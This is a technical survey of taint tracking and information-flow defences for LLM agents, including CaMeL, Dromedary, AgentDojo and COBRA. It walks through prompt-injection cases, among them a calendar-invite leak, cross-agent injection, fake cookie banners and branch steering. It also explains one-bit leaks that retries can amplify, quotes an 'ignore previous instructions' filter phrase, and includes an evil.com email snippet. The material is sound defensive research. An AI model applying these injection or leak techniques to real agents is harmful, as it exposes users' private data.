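# Multi-shot taint tracking across LLM calls: following data provenance when an agent writes code from intermediate results

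## Background: labels, data flow and agents that write code

Taint tracking is a computer-security technique for following data through a program. The system labels each piece of data where it enters, passes the label on to everything the program derives from that data, and checks the label before a sensitive operation runs. The technique belongs to the field of information-flow control. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026), a survey of methods for tracing what AI agents do, lists Denning's 1976 lattice model of secure information flow among the field's foundations.

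Taint tracking has a new use in AI agents. An agent is a program in which a large language model (LLM) chooses actions, such as searching a mailbox or paying a bill, and carries them out through tools, the functions that connect it to other software. Taint tracking is well understood for agents that write one complete program before reading any outside data. Many agents instead run some code, read the results and write more code based on them. Following labels through that cycle is a harder and newer problem.

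### Prompt injection and provenance

Prompt injection is text planted in data that an agent reads, which the model then follows as an instruction. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, an article by David C for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, traces the problem to how models take input. A developer puts trusted instructions and outside content into one prompt, and the model predicts the next token (a fragment of text) from all of it, without separating the two. A job applicant could hide a line in a CV telling the model to approve the CV for interview. Databases had a similar flaw, SQL injection, in which text typed into a web form ran as a command. Parameterised queries fixed it by letting the database engine keep commands and data apart. LLMs can't enforce this separation, and David C thinks they may never be able to.

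The harm depends on what the model can do. *Google Gemini Prompt Injection Flaw Exposed Private Calendar Data via Malicious Invites* (The Hacker News, 2026) describes a case from January 2026 in which an attacker sent the victim a calendar invite with instructions in its description. When the victim later asked Google's Gemini an ordinary question about the week's meetings, the model read the invite, wrote a summary of the victim's private meetings into a new calendar event, and gave a harmless reply. In many company set-ups, the attacker could open the new event. Google has since fixed the flaw.

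One defence is to inspect the text with a filter or a second model that looks for attacks. David C warns against relying on filters for phrases like "ignore previous instructions", since an attacker can reword an attack in endless ways. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, call this approach an arms race that guarantees nothing. Taint tracking instead uses provenance, meaning where the data came from. In the calendar case, a tracker would mark the invite as untrusted because an outsider wrote it, without having to judge whether it looked malicious. It would also mark whatever the model produced after reading the invite as untrusted, and refuse to write private meetings into an event that outsiders can open. An attacker could not change the label by rewording the invite. The drawback is that an honest invite from the same outsider gets the same treatment.

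### Sources, sinks and the join

In *Ghost in the Agent*, Cai, Wen and colleagues (2026) define a source as any tool whose return value may contain content an attacker controls, such as a web search or an email reader. A sink is any tool whose use may affect security, such as one that sends email or executes code. When the concern is secrecy, the sources are instead tools that return private data, such as a company database search, even if that data is trustworthy. A web search is not a source in this sense because its results are public, though untrustworthy.

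A label therefore has two parts. Integrity records how far to trust the data, in the simplest scheme as trusted (T) or untrusted (U). Confidentiality records who may see it, either as public or secret or, more finely, as a set of permitted readers. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, treat the two parts as a pair. Anything derived from two pieces of data gets the join of their labels, written ⊔, which works on each part separately:

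$$(c_1, i_1) \sqcup (c_2, i_2) = (c_1 \sqcup c_2,\; i_1 \sqcup i_2)$$

For integrity, $i_1 \sqcup i_2$ is U if either input is U. For reader sets, $c_1 \sqcup c_2 = c_1 \cap c_2$, because only someone who may read both inputs may read the result.

An example comes from Microsoft's *Information-flow control*, an article on building labels into the company's agent software. Alex asks an agent to deal with unanswered email. A message from Priya, which only she and Alex may read, previews the quarterly sales figures. Another comes from Marco, who is curious about the figures but has no clearance to see them yet. Suppose, in addition, that Alex's system trusts Priya's mail and distrusts Marco's. Once the agent has read both messages, anything it writes carries the label

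$$(\{\text{Alex, Priya}\}, T) \sqcup (\{\text{Alex, Marco}\}, U) = (\{\text{Alex}\}, U)$$

and the system stops a reply to Marco, who is not in the reader set. Nobody has attacked anyone here. The model could have leaked the figures through a plain mistake, and the check would have caught that as well. Had Priya copied Marco in, the reader set would be {Alex, Marco} and the reply could go out.

Costa and colleagues give two basic policies for the check at the sink. A consequential action may run only if the choice of tool and all its arguments are trusted. Data may go out through a channel only if everyone on that channel is in the data's reader set. The second policy, which protects confidentiality, does not stop prompt injection on its own, since planted text could still trigger the action, but it limits what the action can reveal.

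Real work also needs exceptions, in which a system deliberately marks data as less secret (declassification) or more trusted (endorsement). These exceptions can be limited. Under Microsoft's sample policy for posting to a Teams channel, the agent may share text with people outside the text's reader set if it made the request in a trusted context. Otherwise it has to ask a person, which prevents an injected instruction from triggering the exception by itself.

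### Explicit and implicit flows

So far labels have followed data that a program copies or combines, which is an explicit flow. Influence can also travel without any copying. Garby and colleagues give this program, in which the account balance is secret:

```
if account.balance > threshold:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

The text "rich!" is a constant in the program and does not derive from the balance, so a tracker that checked only the arguments would let the email through. But the recipient can infer from the email's arrival that the balance is above the threshold. This is an implicit flow, in which the secret affects which branch runs. Integrity has a similar problem, since an untrusted condition would let an attacker decide whether the email is sent.

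The standard remedy is a program-counter label, which is the join of the labels of all the decisions that led to the code now running. The interpreter raises this label to secret when it enters the branch above, because the condition reads a secret value. The check at `send_email` then joins the program-counter label with the labels of the arguments and blocks the call.

That remedy has a classic gap, which Garby and colleagues credit to Fenton. A monitor that raises labels only as statements run cannot raise a label for a statement the program skips. If a secret condition causes the program to skip an assignment, the variable keeps its old value and public label, even though that value now reveals the condition.

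Researchers disagree about how much of this a system should catch. The strong guarantee is noninterference, which means that changing data with a given label cannot change any output that lacks that label. Costa and colleagues consider it too restrictive for agents, because it would forbid almost any publicly visible action once a tool had read something secret. They settle for explicit secrecy, which covers copying and combining data but not what an observer can infer from the order of tool calls. Garby and colleagues do prove a form of noninterference, but it allows an observer to learn something from a program's failure to finish.

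Implicit flows are harder to detect when they pass through a language model. Cai and colleagues imagine an email whose mention of the word "urgent" leads the agent to run a particular tool. In an ordinary program that would be an `if` statement, and an interpreter could raise the program-counter label on reaching it. Inside a model, the decision happens in the network's weights, where an interpreter can't observe it. Costa and colleagues therefore cautiously label each model response with the join of the labels of everything in its prompt. An agent that holds one long conversation then has a single context label for everything the model has seen so far. This rule is safe but imprecise, and it leads to label creep, in which labels spread until the policy blocks almost every useful action. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) calls this problem label explosion.

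### Agents that act by writing code

In the older design, a model requests one tool call at a time from a fixed list. A banking agent might have tools to read a balance and transfer money, each with its own safeguards. Coding agents write, run and debug their own scripts, and *Can Coding Agents Be General Agents?* (2026) describes how this could let them work in almost any software environment. *Understanding the Architecture of Coding Agents* (2026) examines a prototype whose central loop takes only 18 lines. The loop prompts the model for its next tool request, runs it, records the output in memory, and repeats until the model's request is to finish. *Code as Agent Harness* (Fu, Wei and colleagues, 2026), a survey of such systems, describes agents that create, run, revise and keep pieces of code while they work, and lists Anthropic's Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex among the representative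 systems.

The pattern has also spread beyond software development to the general interfaces that AI companies sell. In *Programmatic tool calling*, a page of Anthropic's developer documentation, the model writes a Python program that calls tools as functions. The program runs in a container, an isolated workspace, and only its final output goes back to the model. To check the expenses of 20 employees, one script can make all 20 lookups and return only the people who went over budget. On web-research benchmarks, Anthropic measured an average performance gain of 11 percent with 24 percent fewer input tokens.

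Keeping intermediate results away from the model also reduces its exposure to planted text, but only partly. One of Anthropic's sample programs fetches a server log and prints the last ten lines that contain the word "ERROR". Anyone who can add such a line to the log can put text in front of the model.

OpenAI's *Programmatic Tool Calling* documents a similar feature in JavaScript, but it handles state differently, which matters for labels. OpenAI runs each program in a fresh runtime with no JavaScript state from earlier programs. Anthropic lets a developer reuse a container to keep state, and can restore an idle container for up to 30 days after its creation. OpenAI also advises direct tool calls when each result should influence the model's next decision. The next action is then a tool call instead of a program, but the model still chooses it after reading the last result.

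### Single-shot planning and multi-shot execution

The planner is the model that decides which tools to call and writes the program. In single-shot planning, it writes the whole program in one call, before the agent reads any outside data. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard et al., 2026) describes such a program for agents that operate a desktop computer. The program has to contain a branch for every situation the planner expects. While it runs, a separate quarantined model with no tools reads the screen and returns values to the program. In multi-shot execution, the agent alternates between running code and calling the planner to write more.

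In multi-shot execution, a shot is one call to the planner that produces a program. The term is unrelated to few-shot prompting, which means putting worked examples in a model's prompt.

Suppose a user asks an agent to find out why last night's software build failed and to repair it. In multi-shot execution, the planner's first program prints the end of the build log. The planner reads this output, finds an error in a particular file, and writes a second program to edit that file. A single-shot planner would have to write the repair without seeing the log, with a branch for each cause it could predict. This is more secure because the program's text depends only on the user's request. In the multi-shot run, the text of the repair program also depends on the log, so anyone who could write to the log could influence it.

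### AgentDojo

Costa et al. and Garby et al. both test their systems on AgentDojo, a benchmark that Debenedetti, Zhang et al. introduced in *AgentDojo* (2024). It simulates an office workspace, a Slack messaging team, a travel agency and a bank. The original version has 97 user tasks, such as paying the bill described in a text file, and 27 attacker goals, such as sending as much money as possible to the attacker's account. Pairing every task with every goal in the same environment gives 629 security cases, each with an injection planted in an email, a file or other content the agent will read. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) gives the number of combinations as over 900.

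AgentDojo measures utility, the share of user tasks that the agent completes, and attack success rate, the share of cases in which the agent carries out the attacker's goal. Researchers report utility both with and without attacks. Under attack, a case counts only if the agent finishes the user's task with no harmful side effects. Ordinary code computes both measures by inspecting the final state of the simulated environment, because a model acting as judge might be misled by the same injection. In 2024, the tested models solved fewer than 66 percent of tasks without any attack, and attacks on the best-performing agents succeeded in fewer than 25 percent of cases.

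A low attack success rate on AgentDojo shows that the particular attacks failed. It cannot establish noninterference, because the benchmark would not record a one-bit leak through a branch unless that leak was the attacker's goal. Its tasks are also short. Foerster and colleagues found that single-shot plans for AgentDojo averaged about 52 lines and five tool calls, compared with 213 lines and 41 calls for their desktop plans. Good results on AgentDojo are therefore weak evidence about long multi-shot runs.

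### Where a label can go missing

Label loss occurs when a value depends on tainted data but no longer carries the label. An agent that writes code from intermediate results can lose labels at three points.

- **The model call.** Labelled text goes into the prompt and plain tokens come out. The surrounding software has to give the response a label, whether by joining everything in the prompt or by some finer estimate of what influenced it.
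- **The program the model writes.** Its constants, its branches and its choice of tools may all derive from what the planner has read. Garby and colleagues handle this by running generated code with the conversation's label as its program-counter label. If the software treated the same code as fresh and trusted, an instruction planted in a build log could come back as a trusted command.
- **The state left between runs.** Cai and colleagues tested an agent that stored a confidential revenue forecast in its memory in one session and, three days later, copied it into a report. A tracker whose labels lasted only as long as a session had nothing to connect the report to the forecast. Variables and files in a reused container raise the same difficulty.

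## Writing the whole program before reading any data

Single-shot planning is the easiest setting for taint tracking, because the planner chooses the agent's actions before the agent opens an email or a web page that might contain planted text.

### Two models and an interpreter

The design builds on the dual-LLM pattern, which Simon Willison proposed in 2023. In this pattern, the planner never reads untrusted text, and the quarantined model that reads it has no tools. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler et al., 2026) illustrates the split with a request to find meeting notes in Google Drive and send a summary to a colleague. The planner arranges the search and the sending, and the quarantined model writes the summary. An instruction planted in the notes could spoil the summary, but the quarantined model cannot send anything itself.

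The leading system of this kind is CaMeL (Capabilities for Machine Learning), which Debenedetti and colleagues introduced in 2025. It handles a request in five steps:

1. The planner receives the request and a description of each tool, and writes a Python program. The descriptions must include the format of each tool's results, because the program has to take apart data that the planner will never see.
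2. A custom interpreter runs the program. It stores tool results in variables and keeps them out of the planner's prompt.
3. Where the program needs to make sense of free text, it passes the text to the quarantined model along with a schema, which fixes the form of the answer (a date, say, or an email address).
4. The interpreter tags every value with its sources and its permitted readers. CaMeL calls these tags capabilities, and they do the job of labels.
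5. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, a Python function that inspects the tags on the arguments and allows or blocks the call.

When the program combines values, the interpreter joins their labels. The same rule can apply to a call to the quarantined model if everything in the prompt counts as an input. This rule causes label creep in long conversations, but the problem is smaller here because each quarantined call has its own prompt, containing only what the program put there.

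### A reminder email in Dromedary

Microsoft's *Dromedary* is a small replication of CaMeL, published as a research demonstration with a warning against production use. Its documentation shows two runs of nearly the same task. In the first, the user asks the agent to find Bob's address in the last email received and send him a reminder of tomorrow's meeting. Condensed, and with shorter variable names, the planner's program is:

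```
inbox = get_received_emails()
last = inbox[-1]
address = query_ai_assistant("Find Bob's address: " + last.body, EmailStr)
send_email([address], "Reminder", "Hi Bob, ...")
```

The function `query_ai_assistant` calls the quarantined model, and `EmailStr` requires the answer to be an email address. Dromedary records the tools each value came from. In terms of integrity, the values have these labels:

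| Value | Derived from | Integrity |
|---|---|---|
| `inbox`, `last` | received email | untrusted |
| `address` | the quarantined model's reading of `last` | untrusted |
| subject and body | text written by the planner | trusted |

When the program reaches `send_email`, the policy checks the recipient and blocks the call. The error message names `get_received_emails` as the untrusted source and suggests using the contact-search tools instead. Although the address came directly from the quarantined model, the interpreter had tracked its origin through the model call. The schema alone would not have protected the user, because an attacker's address is also a valid email address.

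The user then asks the agent to look up Bob Wilson and send him the reminder. The new program calls `search_contacts_by_name("Bob Wilson")`, takes the first match and sends the same message. The policy accepts addresses from the contact list, and the email goes out.

Neither run involved an attack. The first email may well have contained Bob's real address, but the policy blocked it because anyone can send an email. The contact list is trusted only because the policy's author decided to trust it. If the user's mail software added every sender to the contacts automatically, an outsider could add a false Bob Wilson and the check would pass. The security proofs in Dongol's *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) explicitly assume that attackers cannot write to trusted sources, which rules out trusting a calendar that accepts outsiders' invitations. Labels also don't prevent ordinary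 mistakes. If the user knows two people called Bob Wilson, the program may email the wrong one even when every label is correct.

### Why the labels are easy to keep

The program's text depends only on the request and the tool descriptions, so its constants, conditions and choice of tools all start out trusted. Only values that arrive while the program runs need labels, and the interpreter controls the variables that hold them.

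Writing the whole program first also avoids the problem of a single context label. Suppose Dromedary's second program had also read the inbox to check the time of the meeting. The time would be untrusted, but the address from the contact list would stay trusted, because the interpreter tracks the two values separately. Under a single context label, the address would become untrusted too.

Branches need more care because of implicit flows, but the interpreter can at least read the label of each condition. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) report in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* that CaMeL blocks the email that would reveal whether an account balance is above a threshold, although they also found leaks in its tracking.

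### What a fixed program guarantees

The main guarantee is control-flow integrity. Peters-Gill and colleagues define a control-flow plan as a program, fixed in advance, that determines which tools run and in what order based on the values the tools return. By their definition, an agent has control-flow integrity if it can only follow a plan that comes from the user's instruction and other trusted information. Untrusted data may select among the plan's branches but can't add a new one. An injected instruction to "forward this to everyone" has no effect unless the planner had already written a call that forwards email.

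Fixing the plan in advance isn't enough if the model that reads the data can also call tools. Dongol describes an agent whose plan is to look up the user's account number, read an email and show a summary. The plan sends nothing, but if the summarising model can fetch web pages, the email can tell it to fetch a URL on the attacker's site that ends with the account number.

Dongol's standard for such agents compares each one with a reference agent that runs the same plan under the same checks, but whose model never obeys untrusted text. An agent is *relatively secure* if an attacker can't use injections to tell apart any two secrets that the reference agent would have kept indistinguishable. Suppose a user has authorised an assistant to send her calendar to anyone who requests a meeting. The assistant can still meet the standard if an injection makes it send the calendar, because an honest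 request would have disclosed the same information, but not if the injection makes it send a password-reset code as well. Noninterference would reject this assistant outright.

Dongol points out a weakness in the standard. If the reference agent tells an attacker whether a guess at a secret is right, then for any two secrets, some guess distinguishes them, so an injection that sends the entire secret still counts as relatively secure.

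Using the proof assistant Isabelle/HOL, Dongol proves that an agent of this kind is relatively secure if, at the first untrusted read, a monitor permanently withdraws every tool an injection could call. The result assumes that each injection makes a single call, on a schedule fixed in advance, and that the attacker sees the content and order of messages but not their timing. If the plan reads the email, then a secret, and only then drops the sending tool, an injected call can use the tool before it is dropped. The rule also limits what the agent can do, since an agent that has lost its email tool can't reply to the email it has just read.

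CaMeL avoids that drawback because the program keeps its tools and the quarantined model never has any. In Dongol's model of the dual-LLM pattern, an injection can corrupt only the quarantined model's answer. That answer may still depend on everything in the prompt. If the program sends the quarantined model a secret and an untrusted email together, the answer could contain the secret disguised as an ordinary value, so the interpreter has to label the answer as both secret and untrusted.

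All of this depends on the planner reading only trusted text, and tool descriptions can easily break that condition. In tool poisoning, a malicious server hides an instruction in the description of one of its tools. A planner that read the description would write the attacker's instruction into a program that the interpreter treats as fully trusted. In *Operationalizing CaMeL*, Tallam and Miller (2025) raise the same concern about the user's request, which may contain text that someone else persuaded the user to paste in. They also note that CaMeL doesn't inspect what it shows the user, so a summary could repeat a planted instruction for a person to follow. They add that if a secret number sets how many times a loop fetches a web page, anyone who can read the server's log can learn that number.

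The guarantee can also fail when agents delegate work to each other. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system of three CaMeL agents, planted an instruction in a database of job applicants, and asked the system to send a summary of the applicants to Julie on Slack. The coordinating agent's program kept the database text away from its own planner, but pasted the summary into a message asking a second agent to send it. The second agent's planner treated that message as its user's request and wrote a program that also emailed the applicants' data to an outside address.

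Their remedy divides every message that one agent sends another into an instruction, which the receiving planner reads, and a set of variables, which it doesn't. The interpreter refuses any instruction that depends on a tool's output. In tests on a multi-agent version of AgentDojo with five models, attacks succeeded in 12.9 percent of cases on average without CaMeL, 0.2 percent with CaMeL on each agent separately, and none with the divided messages.

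### Untrusted arguments

Control-flow integrity would not have stopped Dromedary's first email. The user asked for a reminder, the planner wrote a call to `send_email`, and that call ran where the plan put it. Only the recipient was uncertain. The labels and policies defend against bad values in legitimate calls, and they add more overhead than the split between the two models.

Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL three times on each of AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks to measure its effect on task completion. With policies off, it completed 67 percent of runs using GPT-5.2 and 71 percent using MiMo-v2.5. With policies on, it completed 37.5 percent with either model. The margins of error are wide, about 27 points either way for the 37.5 percent figure. Even with policies off, CaMeL resisted the attack in 239 of 240 runs with GPT-5.2 and 378 of 382 with MiMo-v2.5. With policies on, it resisted every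 attack.

On this benchmark, the split stopped nearly all the attacks, while the policies stopped the last few and cut the number of completed tasks by close to half. AgentDojo probably undervalues the policies, because its injections are designed to trigger actions outside the user's task, which a fixed program is good at preventing. An attacker who only wanted to change a payee's account number in a genuine invoice would need no new action, so a fixed program alone would not prevent the attack.

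Foerster and colleagues note that writing the policies takes expert knowledge, that no method derives the rules automatically, and that users differ in what they are willing to share. Tallam and Miller expect a company with hundreds of tools to end up with duplicated and inconsistent rules.

### Branch steering

Untrusted data can also decide which part of a program runs. Suppose the user says, "If Bob's last email says the meeting is off, delete it from my calendar; otherwise send him a reminder." The planner writes both branches. An attacker who can pass off an email as Bob's can get the meeting deleted without injecting any instruction or supplying any argument to the delete call. Foerster and colleagues named this kind of attack branch steering.

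A program-counter label would show that the deletion depended on an untrusted condition, and a policy could then block the deletion. But the same policy would also block it when Bob had genuinely cancelled, even though the user wanted the deletion to depend on the email. This is why control-flow integrity permits branch steering, which strict noninterference would forbid.

The danger grows with the number of branches. Foerster and colleagues counted an average of 3.7 branches per program for AgentDojo tasks and 39.7 for desktop tasks, where the planner has to allow for pop-ups, failed clicks and unfamiliar pages. Many desktop plans begin with a check for a cookie notice to dismiss. The researchers put a fake notice inside an advertisement, and the quarantined model returned its position, so the agent clicked it and landed on the attacker's site. Comparing the screenshot with the page's code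 exposed the fake in some static advertisements, where the code labelled the frame as an advertisement. The comparison failed on banners that replaced that frame. In a second attack, small changes to an advertisement's pixels misled the quarantined model and also got past an independent model checking its answer.

These tests ran without data-flow policies, partly because such policies are hard to write for a desktop. A policy can check the recipient of a `send_email` call, but a click has only coordinates, and the same click might close a window or confirm a payment.

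*Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (Zingrillo, Foerster and colleagues, 2026) moves the check to the network, where a click that approves a loan becomes a web request to a recognisable address. Before the agent sees any page, the paper's system, COBRA, limits which sites and tools each branch may use and which values it may submit. If the task needs a sensitive value that no trusted source can supply, COBRA asks the user for it during planning.

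They tested COBRA on STEER-Bench, their own set of 101 tasks that includes bank transfers and changes to medication doses. On the cases that ordinary agents could also run, attacks succeeded 94.4 percent of the time against a standard agent and 89.5 percent against a dual-LLM agent without COBRA's limits. None succeeded against COBRA, which kept 97 percent of the dual-LLM agent's performance on harmless tasks.

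That zero means that no harmful action broke the limits in force at that point, which is how the benchmark defines a successful attack. A page can still steer COBRA into a branch by supplying values that satisfy those limits, so the protection depends on how well the planner wrote them. In the calendar example, a rule that the branch may delete only tomorrow's meeting would protect the rest of the calendar, but the forged email would still cancel that meeting.

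## Where a single program fails

A planner that writes its whole program in advance can include only the steps it foresees. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) sorts users' requests by how much they leave open. A fully specified request gives the action and its details, such as sending Bob £20. A "param-open" request gives the action but leaves a detail to the data, such as paying whatever amount an invoice states. An "action-open" request leaves the action to the data, such as following the instructions in an email. A single program can handle a missing detail by reserving a variable for it. A missing action is harder, because the planner must write the call before it knows which one the task needs.

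### Tasks that need an intermediate result

Suppose a user wants the total refunds from a spreadsheet that a supplier sent. The tool descriptions give CaMeL's planner the format of each tool's results, but not the layout of this file. The program can use the quarantined model to find the refunds column from the header row, which works if the file has such a column. If the supplier records refunds as negative sales, or keeps each month on a separate sheet, the calculation needs different code, but the planner has already written the program.

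Research tasks pose a similar difficulty. An agent looking into a factory closure might find a news story that names the parent company, and only then know to search for that company's accounts. A program can handle part of this with a loop that calls a fixed tool, while the quarantined model reads each result and proposes the next query. *ActGuard* (2026), a defence that audits each tool call before it runs, similarly has its agent predict at each step which tools might come next but not their arguments, because the arguments depend heavily on a result that hasn't arrived yet. The loop fails when a result shows that the agent needs a tool the planner left out, such as a court database. It also lets untrusted text determine every query, so the program still needs labels to stop a query from carrying private data to a search site.

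Debugging is worse, since each run is meant to find out something the programmer didn't know. For the failed software build described earlier, the program could have the quarantined model read the log and write the repair. But then a model that had read untrusted text would be writing the code, which the two-model design is meant to prevent.

Ordinary breakdowns can also make a single program fail. *PreFlect* (2026) describes an agent that looks for likely failures in its plan before acting on it. The agent still replans when progress stalls, because many obstacles, such as a tool that returns nothing, appear only at run time. *Agent Planning Benchmark* (2026) tests complete plans separately from the choice of next steps in a partly finished run. In 300 of its cases, an important tool returns an error, a substitute tool is available, and the model must choose its next action. A single-shot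 planner would need to write the fallback before the tool failed.

In the extreme case, the steps appear only in the data. One of AgentDojo's banking tasks asks the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. When Garby and colleagues ran this task, CaMeL's planner wrote the program in advance as a loop over the file's instructions, with a branch for each tool. But the file's contents can trigger almost any action in such a program, and with CaMeL's policies off, injections succeeded in two runs. In *Kaer*, Mallick, Rose and colleagues (2026) consider this a general problem with fixed plans, because a plan that allows for every course of events becomes either too complex to analyse or so permissive that it invites prompt injection.

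*AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026) measured how a fixed plan affects task completion on tasks like these. By its count, only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require an agent to change its plan in response to what it finds. It adds 60 new tasks that all require this, covering shopping, GitHub and everyday errands. For example, a checkout page might tell the agent to log in first. Without a defence, Claude Sonnet 3.5 completed 60 percent of the tasks, GPT-4o 53 percent, Gemini 2.5 Pro 52 percent and Llama 3.3 70B 10 percent. With CaMeL, none of the four models completed any.

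Committing only to a set of tools was not much better. A defence called Tool Filter has a model decide at the start which tools the task needs and withholds the rest. Completion fell to between 2 and 8 percent because the filter removed tools that looked irrelevant at the start but were needed later.

These are older models, but a stronger planner would face the same obstacle whenever the necessary step appears only in the data. The zero for CaMeL comes from tasks that Li and colleagues designed to require replanning, so it doesn't measure how common such tasks are.

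### Operating a computer from a fixed plan

Operating a computer through its screen combines several of these difficulties, because the planner has no information about which windows are open, where a button is or whether a click will work. An ordinary computer-use agent takes a new screenshot before each action. Foerster and colleagues tested whether an agent could instead plan every action before seeing the screen.

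An adapted version of CaMeL gives the planner a method called NOVA (Navigating via Observation, Verification, and Action). A NOVA program first has the quarantined vision model describe the screen. It then passes the description to `verify_hypothesis`, which compares it with a state the planner predicted, such as "a cookie banner is visible". The program picks a branch based on the result, and only then clicks or types. The planner's instructions also include routines for common situations, such as dismissing a cookie banner or recovering from a failed click.

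The researchers used OSWorld, a benchmark of tasks in real applications such as Chrome, LibreOffice and GIMP. They compared the structure of the resulting plans with that of CaMeL's plans for AgentDojo:

| Average per plan | AgentDojo | OSWorld with NOVA |
|---|---|---|
| Lines of code | 51.8 | 213.3 |
| Tool calls | 4.9 | 41.1 |
| Branches | 3.7 | 39.7 |
| Branches that depend on the quarantined model's answers | 1.9 | 24.2 |

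The desktop plans are about four times as long as the AgentDojo plans but have more than ten times as many branches. Roughly half of their steps are fallbacks that don't run in a given run of the plan. On AgentDojo, 79 percent of branches test something the program already controls, such as a loop counter, compared with only 9 percent on the desktop. Most of the other desktop branches test what is on the screen or whether an action worked.

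The table also shows why nobody could write a separate path for every situation. Twenty-four independent yes-or-no checks have more than 16 million possible combinations of answers. A plan can stay near 200 lines only if most of its branches lead back to a common path, which assumes the same next step suits all of those branches.

The extra branches helped. With a generic prompt and no `verify_hypothesis`, the agent wrote plans that averaged 72 lines and 11 branches, and it solved 11 of 60 tasks within three attempts. It solved 35 of the same 60 with NOVA.

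For most of their tests, Foerster and colleagues chose tasks that a vision model had already solved as an ordinary agent, in one attempt of at most 15 steps. They then gave the same model the quarantined role and had a separate planner write the program:

| Vision model | Tasks solved as an ordinary agent | Of these, solved from a fixed plan in one attempt | Solved within five attempts |
|---|---|---|---|
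| UI-TARS-1.5-7B | 60 | 25 | 39 |
| OpenCUA-32B | 76 | 22 | 48 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 109 | 31 | 62 |

The paper's main claim for large models is that they retain up to 57 percent of their performance. That figure is Claude's 62 out of 109, and it compares five attempts with one. On a single attempt, Claude retained 28 percent.

Choosing tasks this way also excludes any that a fixed plan could solve but the ordinary agent could not. Of the 339 tasks that OSWorld can score automatically, UI-TARS solved 60 as an ordinary agent. With fixed plans, it solved 51 in one attempt and 77 within three. This is a much better result for planning ahead, but partly because a separate, far more capable model did the planning, while the ordinary agent used only the small model.

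In one task, the user asks to "browse the natural products database" while the browser is on drugs.com. The correct route goes through a link for drugs and medications, then a list of drug categories, and finally a link to natural products. Searching the site produces no result with the right title. GPT-5's plan tries the site's search box and, if the next page looks irrelevant, searches the web for a natural products database, which could lead to one on the wrong site. Someone looking at the results page could try a likely link, then go back and try another, but a fixed plan has to describe each of those links before the page appears.

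NOVA works best on surprises that recur across tasks. Any given page may or may not show a cookie banner, but banners are common across the web, so a single routine handles most of them. A particular site's menus need their own branches, and each further click adds pages that the planner has to predict.

### When the planner gets another try

CaMeL is sometimes multi-shot in practice, because an outer loop can ask the planner for another program if one fails. Generated code often needs more than one attempt. Garby and colleagues asked GPT-5.2 to write a factorial function in a small language they had designed, and it produced valid code on the third attempt.

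An error partway through a program may reveal something about outside data, unlike a syntax error caught before the program starts, because the program could already have opened an email or read a bank balance. The planner's next program then depends on what the first one found. An attacker might send an invoice with no amount on it to cause a failure, and so influence the next program without the planner ever reading the invoice. A retry can also repeat an action, such as paying a bill again if the first program paid it and then crashed.

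CaMeL doesn't track how error messages from earlier attempts influence later ones. Its labels exist inside the interpreter, while the retry loop is ordinary Python code outside it. Garby and colleagues point out that each attempt therefore starts with clean labels, even though it depends on those messages. CaMeL's designers acknowledge the problem and censor the messages, but the planner still learns that something went wrong, and there is no proven limit on how much information gets through.

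A policy block creates the same kind of signal. The earlier program tries to email an outsider only if an account balance is above a threshold. If it is, CaMeL blocks the email. Otherwise, the program skips that line and finishes normally. A block therefore reveals that the balance is above the threshold, and this one bit of information reaches the retry loop without a label. A later program could put it in a message that the interpreter treats as public.

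Security researchers normally tolerate a leak of one such bit per run, and guarantees described as termination-insensitive permit it by design. A monitor that stops forbidden actions can't easily hide that it stopped one, and preventing the leak completely would mean ruling out any program that might finish or fail depending on a secret. The damage from one answer is also usually small. For example, an observer who learns that a balance exceeds £10,000 still doesn't know the balance.

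Unlimited retries remove that limit. If each new run can test a different threshold, each answer can halve the remaining range. Since $k$ yes-or-no answers can distinguish up to $2^k$ values, 20 answers are enough to find a whole-pound balance between zero and £1 million. A cap on retries would limit the leak, but the tracker would still not count the leaked bits or label the programs that depend on them.

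This is a gap in CaMeL's guarantee, not evidence of attacks in practice. Exploiting it requires a program that repeatedly changes the threshold. A planner that reads only trusted text would not normally write such a program, but a poisoned tool description could cause it to.

One fix is to move the retry loop inside the tracker, so that each new program carries the label of whatever the failed run read. But a tool such as `send_money` may then reject the program's arguments as untrusted, even if the user asked for the payment. Garby and colleagues avoid this by having their agent rehearse. It tries programs in a simulated environment until one works, and only then runs that program on the real data. Rehearsal can catch coding mistakes, but the planner can't learn from a simulation how a supplier has laid out a real spreadsheet or why last night's build failed.

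Tallam and Miller suggest that a function should return either a value or an error instead of raising an exception. The program could then handle the error itself, and the interpreter could label it, but the planner would still have to write the error handling in advance. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) takes the strictest approach, calling the planner once per request and never reporting a failed plan to it.

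### How much planning ahead can cover

Foerster and colleagues argue from their results that computer tasks depend less on live feedback than they seem to, and that better planners will complete more of them without weakening the security design. A fixed plan also lets a person inspect it before it runs. On a sample of 17 tasks, NOVA used only 1.88 times as many tokens as the ordinary agent.

Some results favor using a fixed program. If 91 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks need no change of plan, a fixed program suits nearly the whole benchmark. On desktop tasks, the choice of planner also made a large difference. With UI-TARS reading the screen in every case, plans by GPT-5 solved 12 of the 17 tasks within five attempts, while plans by Kimi K2 and by DeepSeek-R1 solved 4 each. The weaker planners tended to leave out fallbacks for unexpected screens, and newer planners could well do better than GPT-5.

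But GPT-5 solved only 3 of those 17 tasks on its first attempt. Scoring by the best of five attempts assumes that something can recognise the successful one and that the failures do no harm, but on a real computer a bad plan might already have deleted a file or sent a message. The planner can at least write all five plans before any of them runs, so the extra attempts don't feed outside data into new code as CaMeL's retry loop does.

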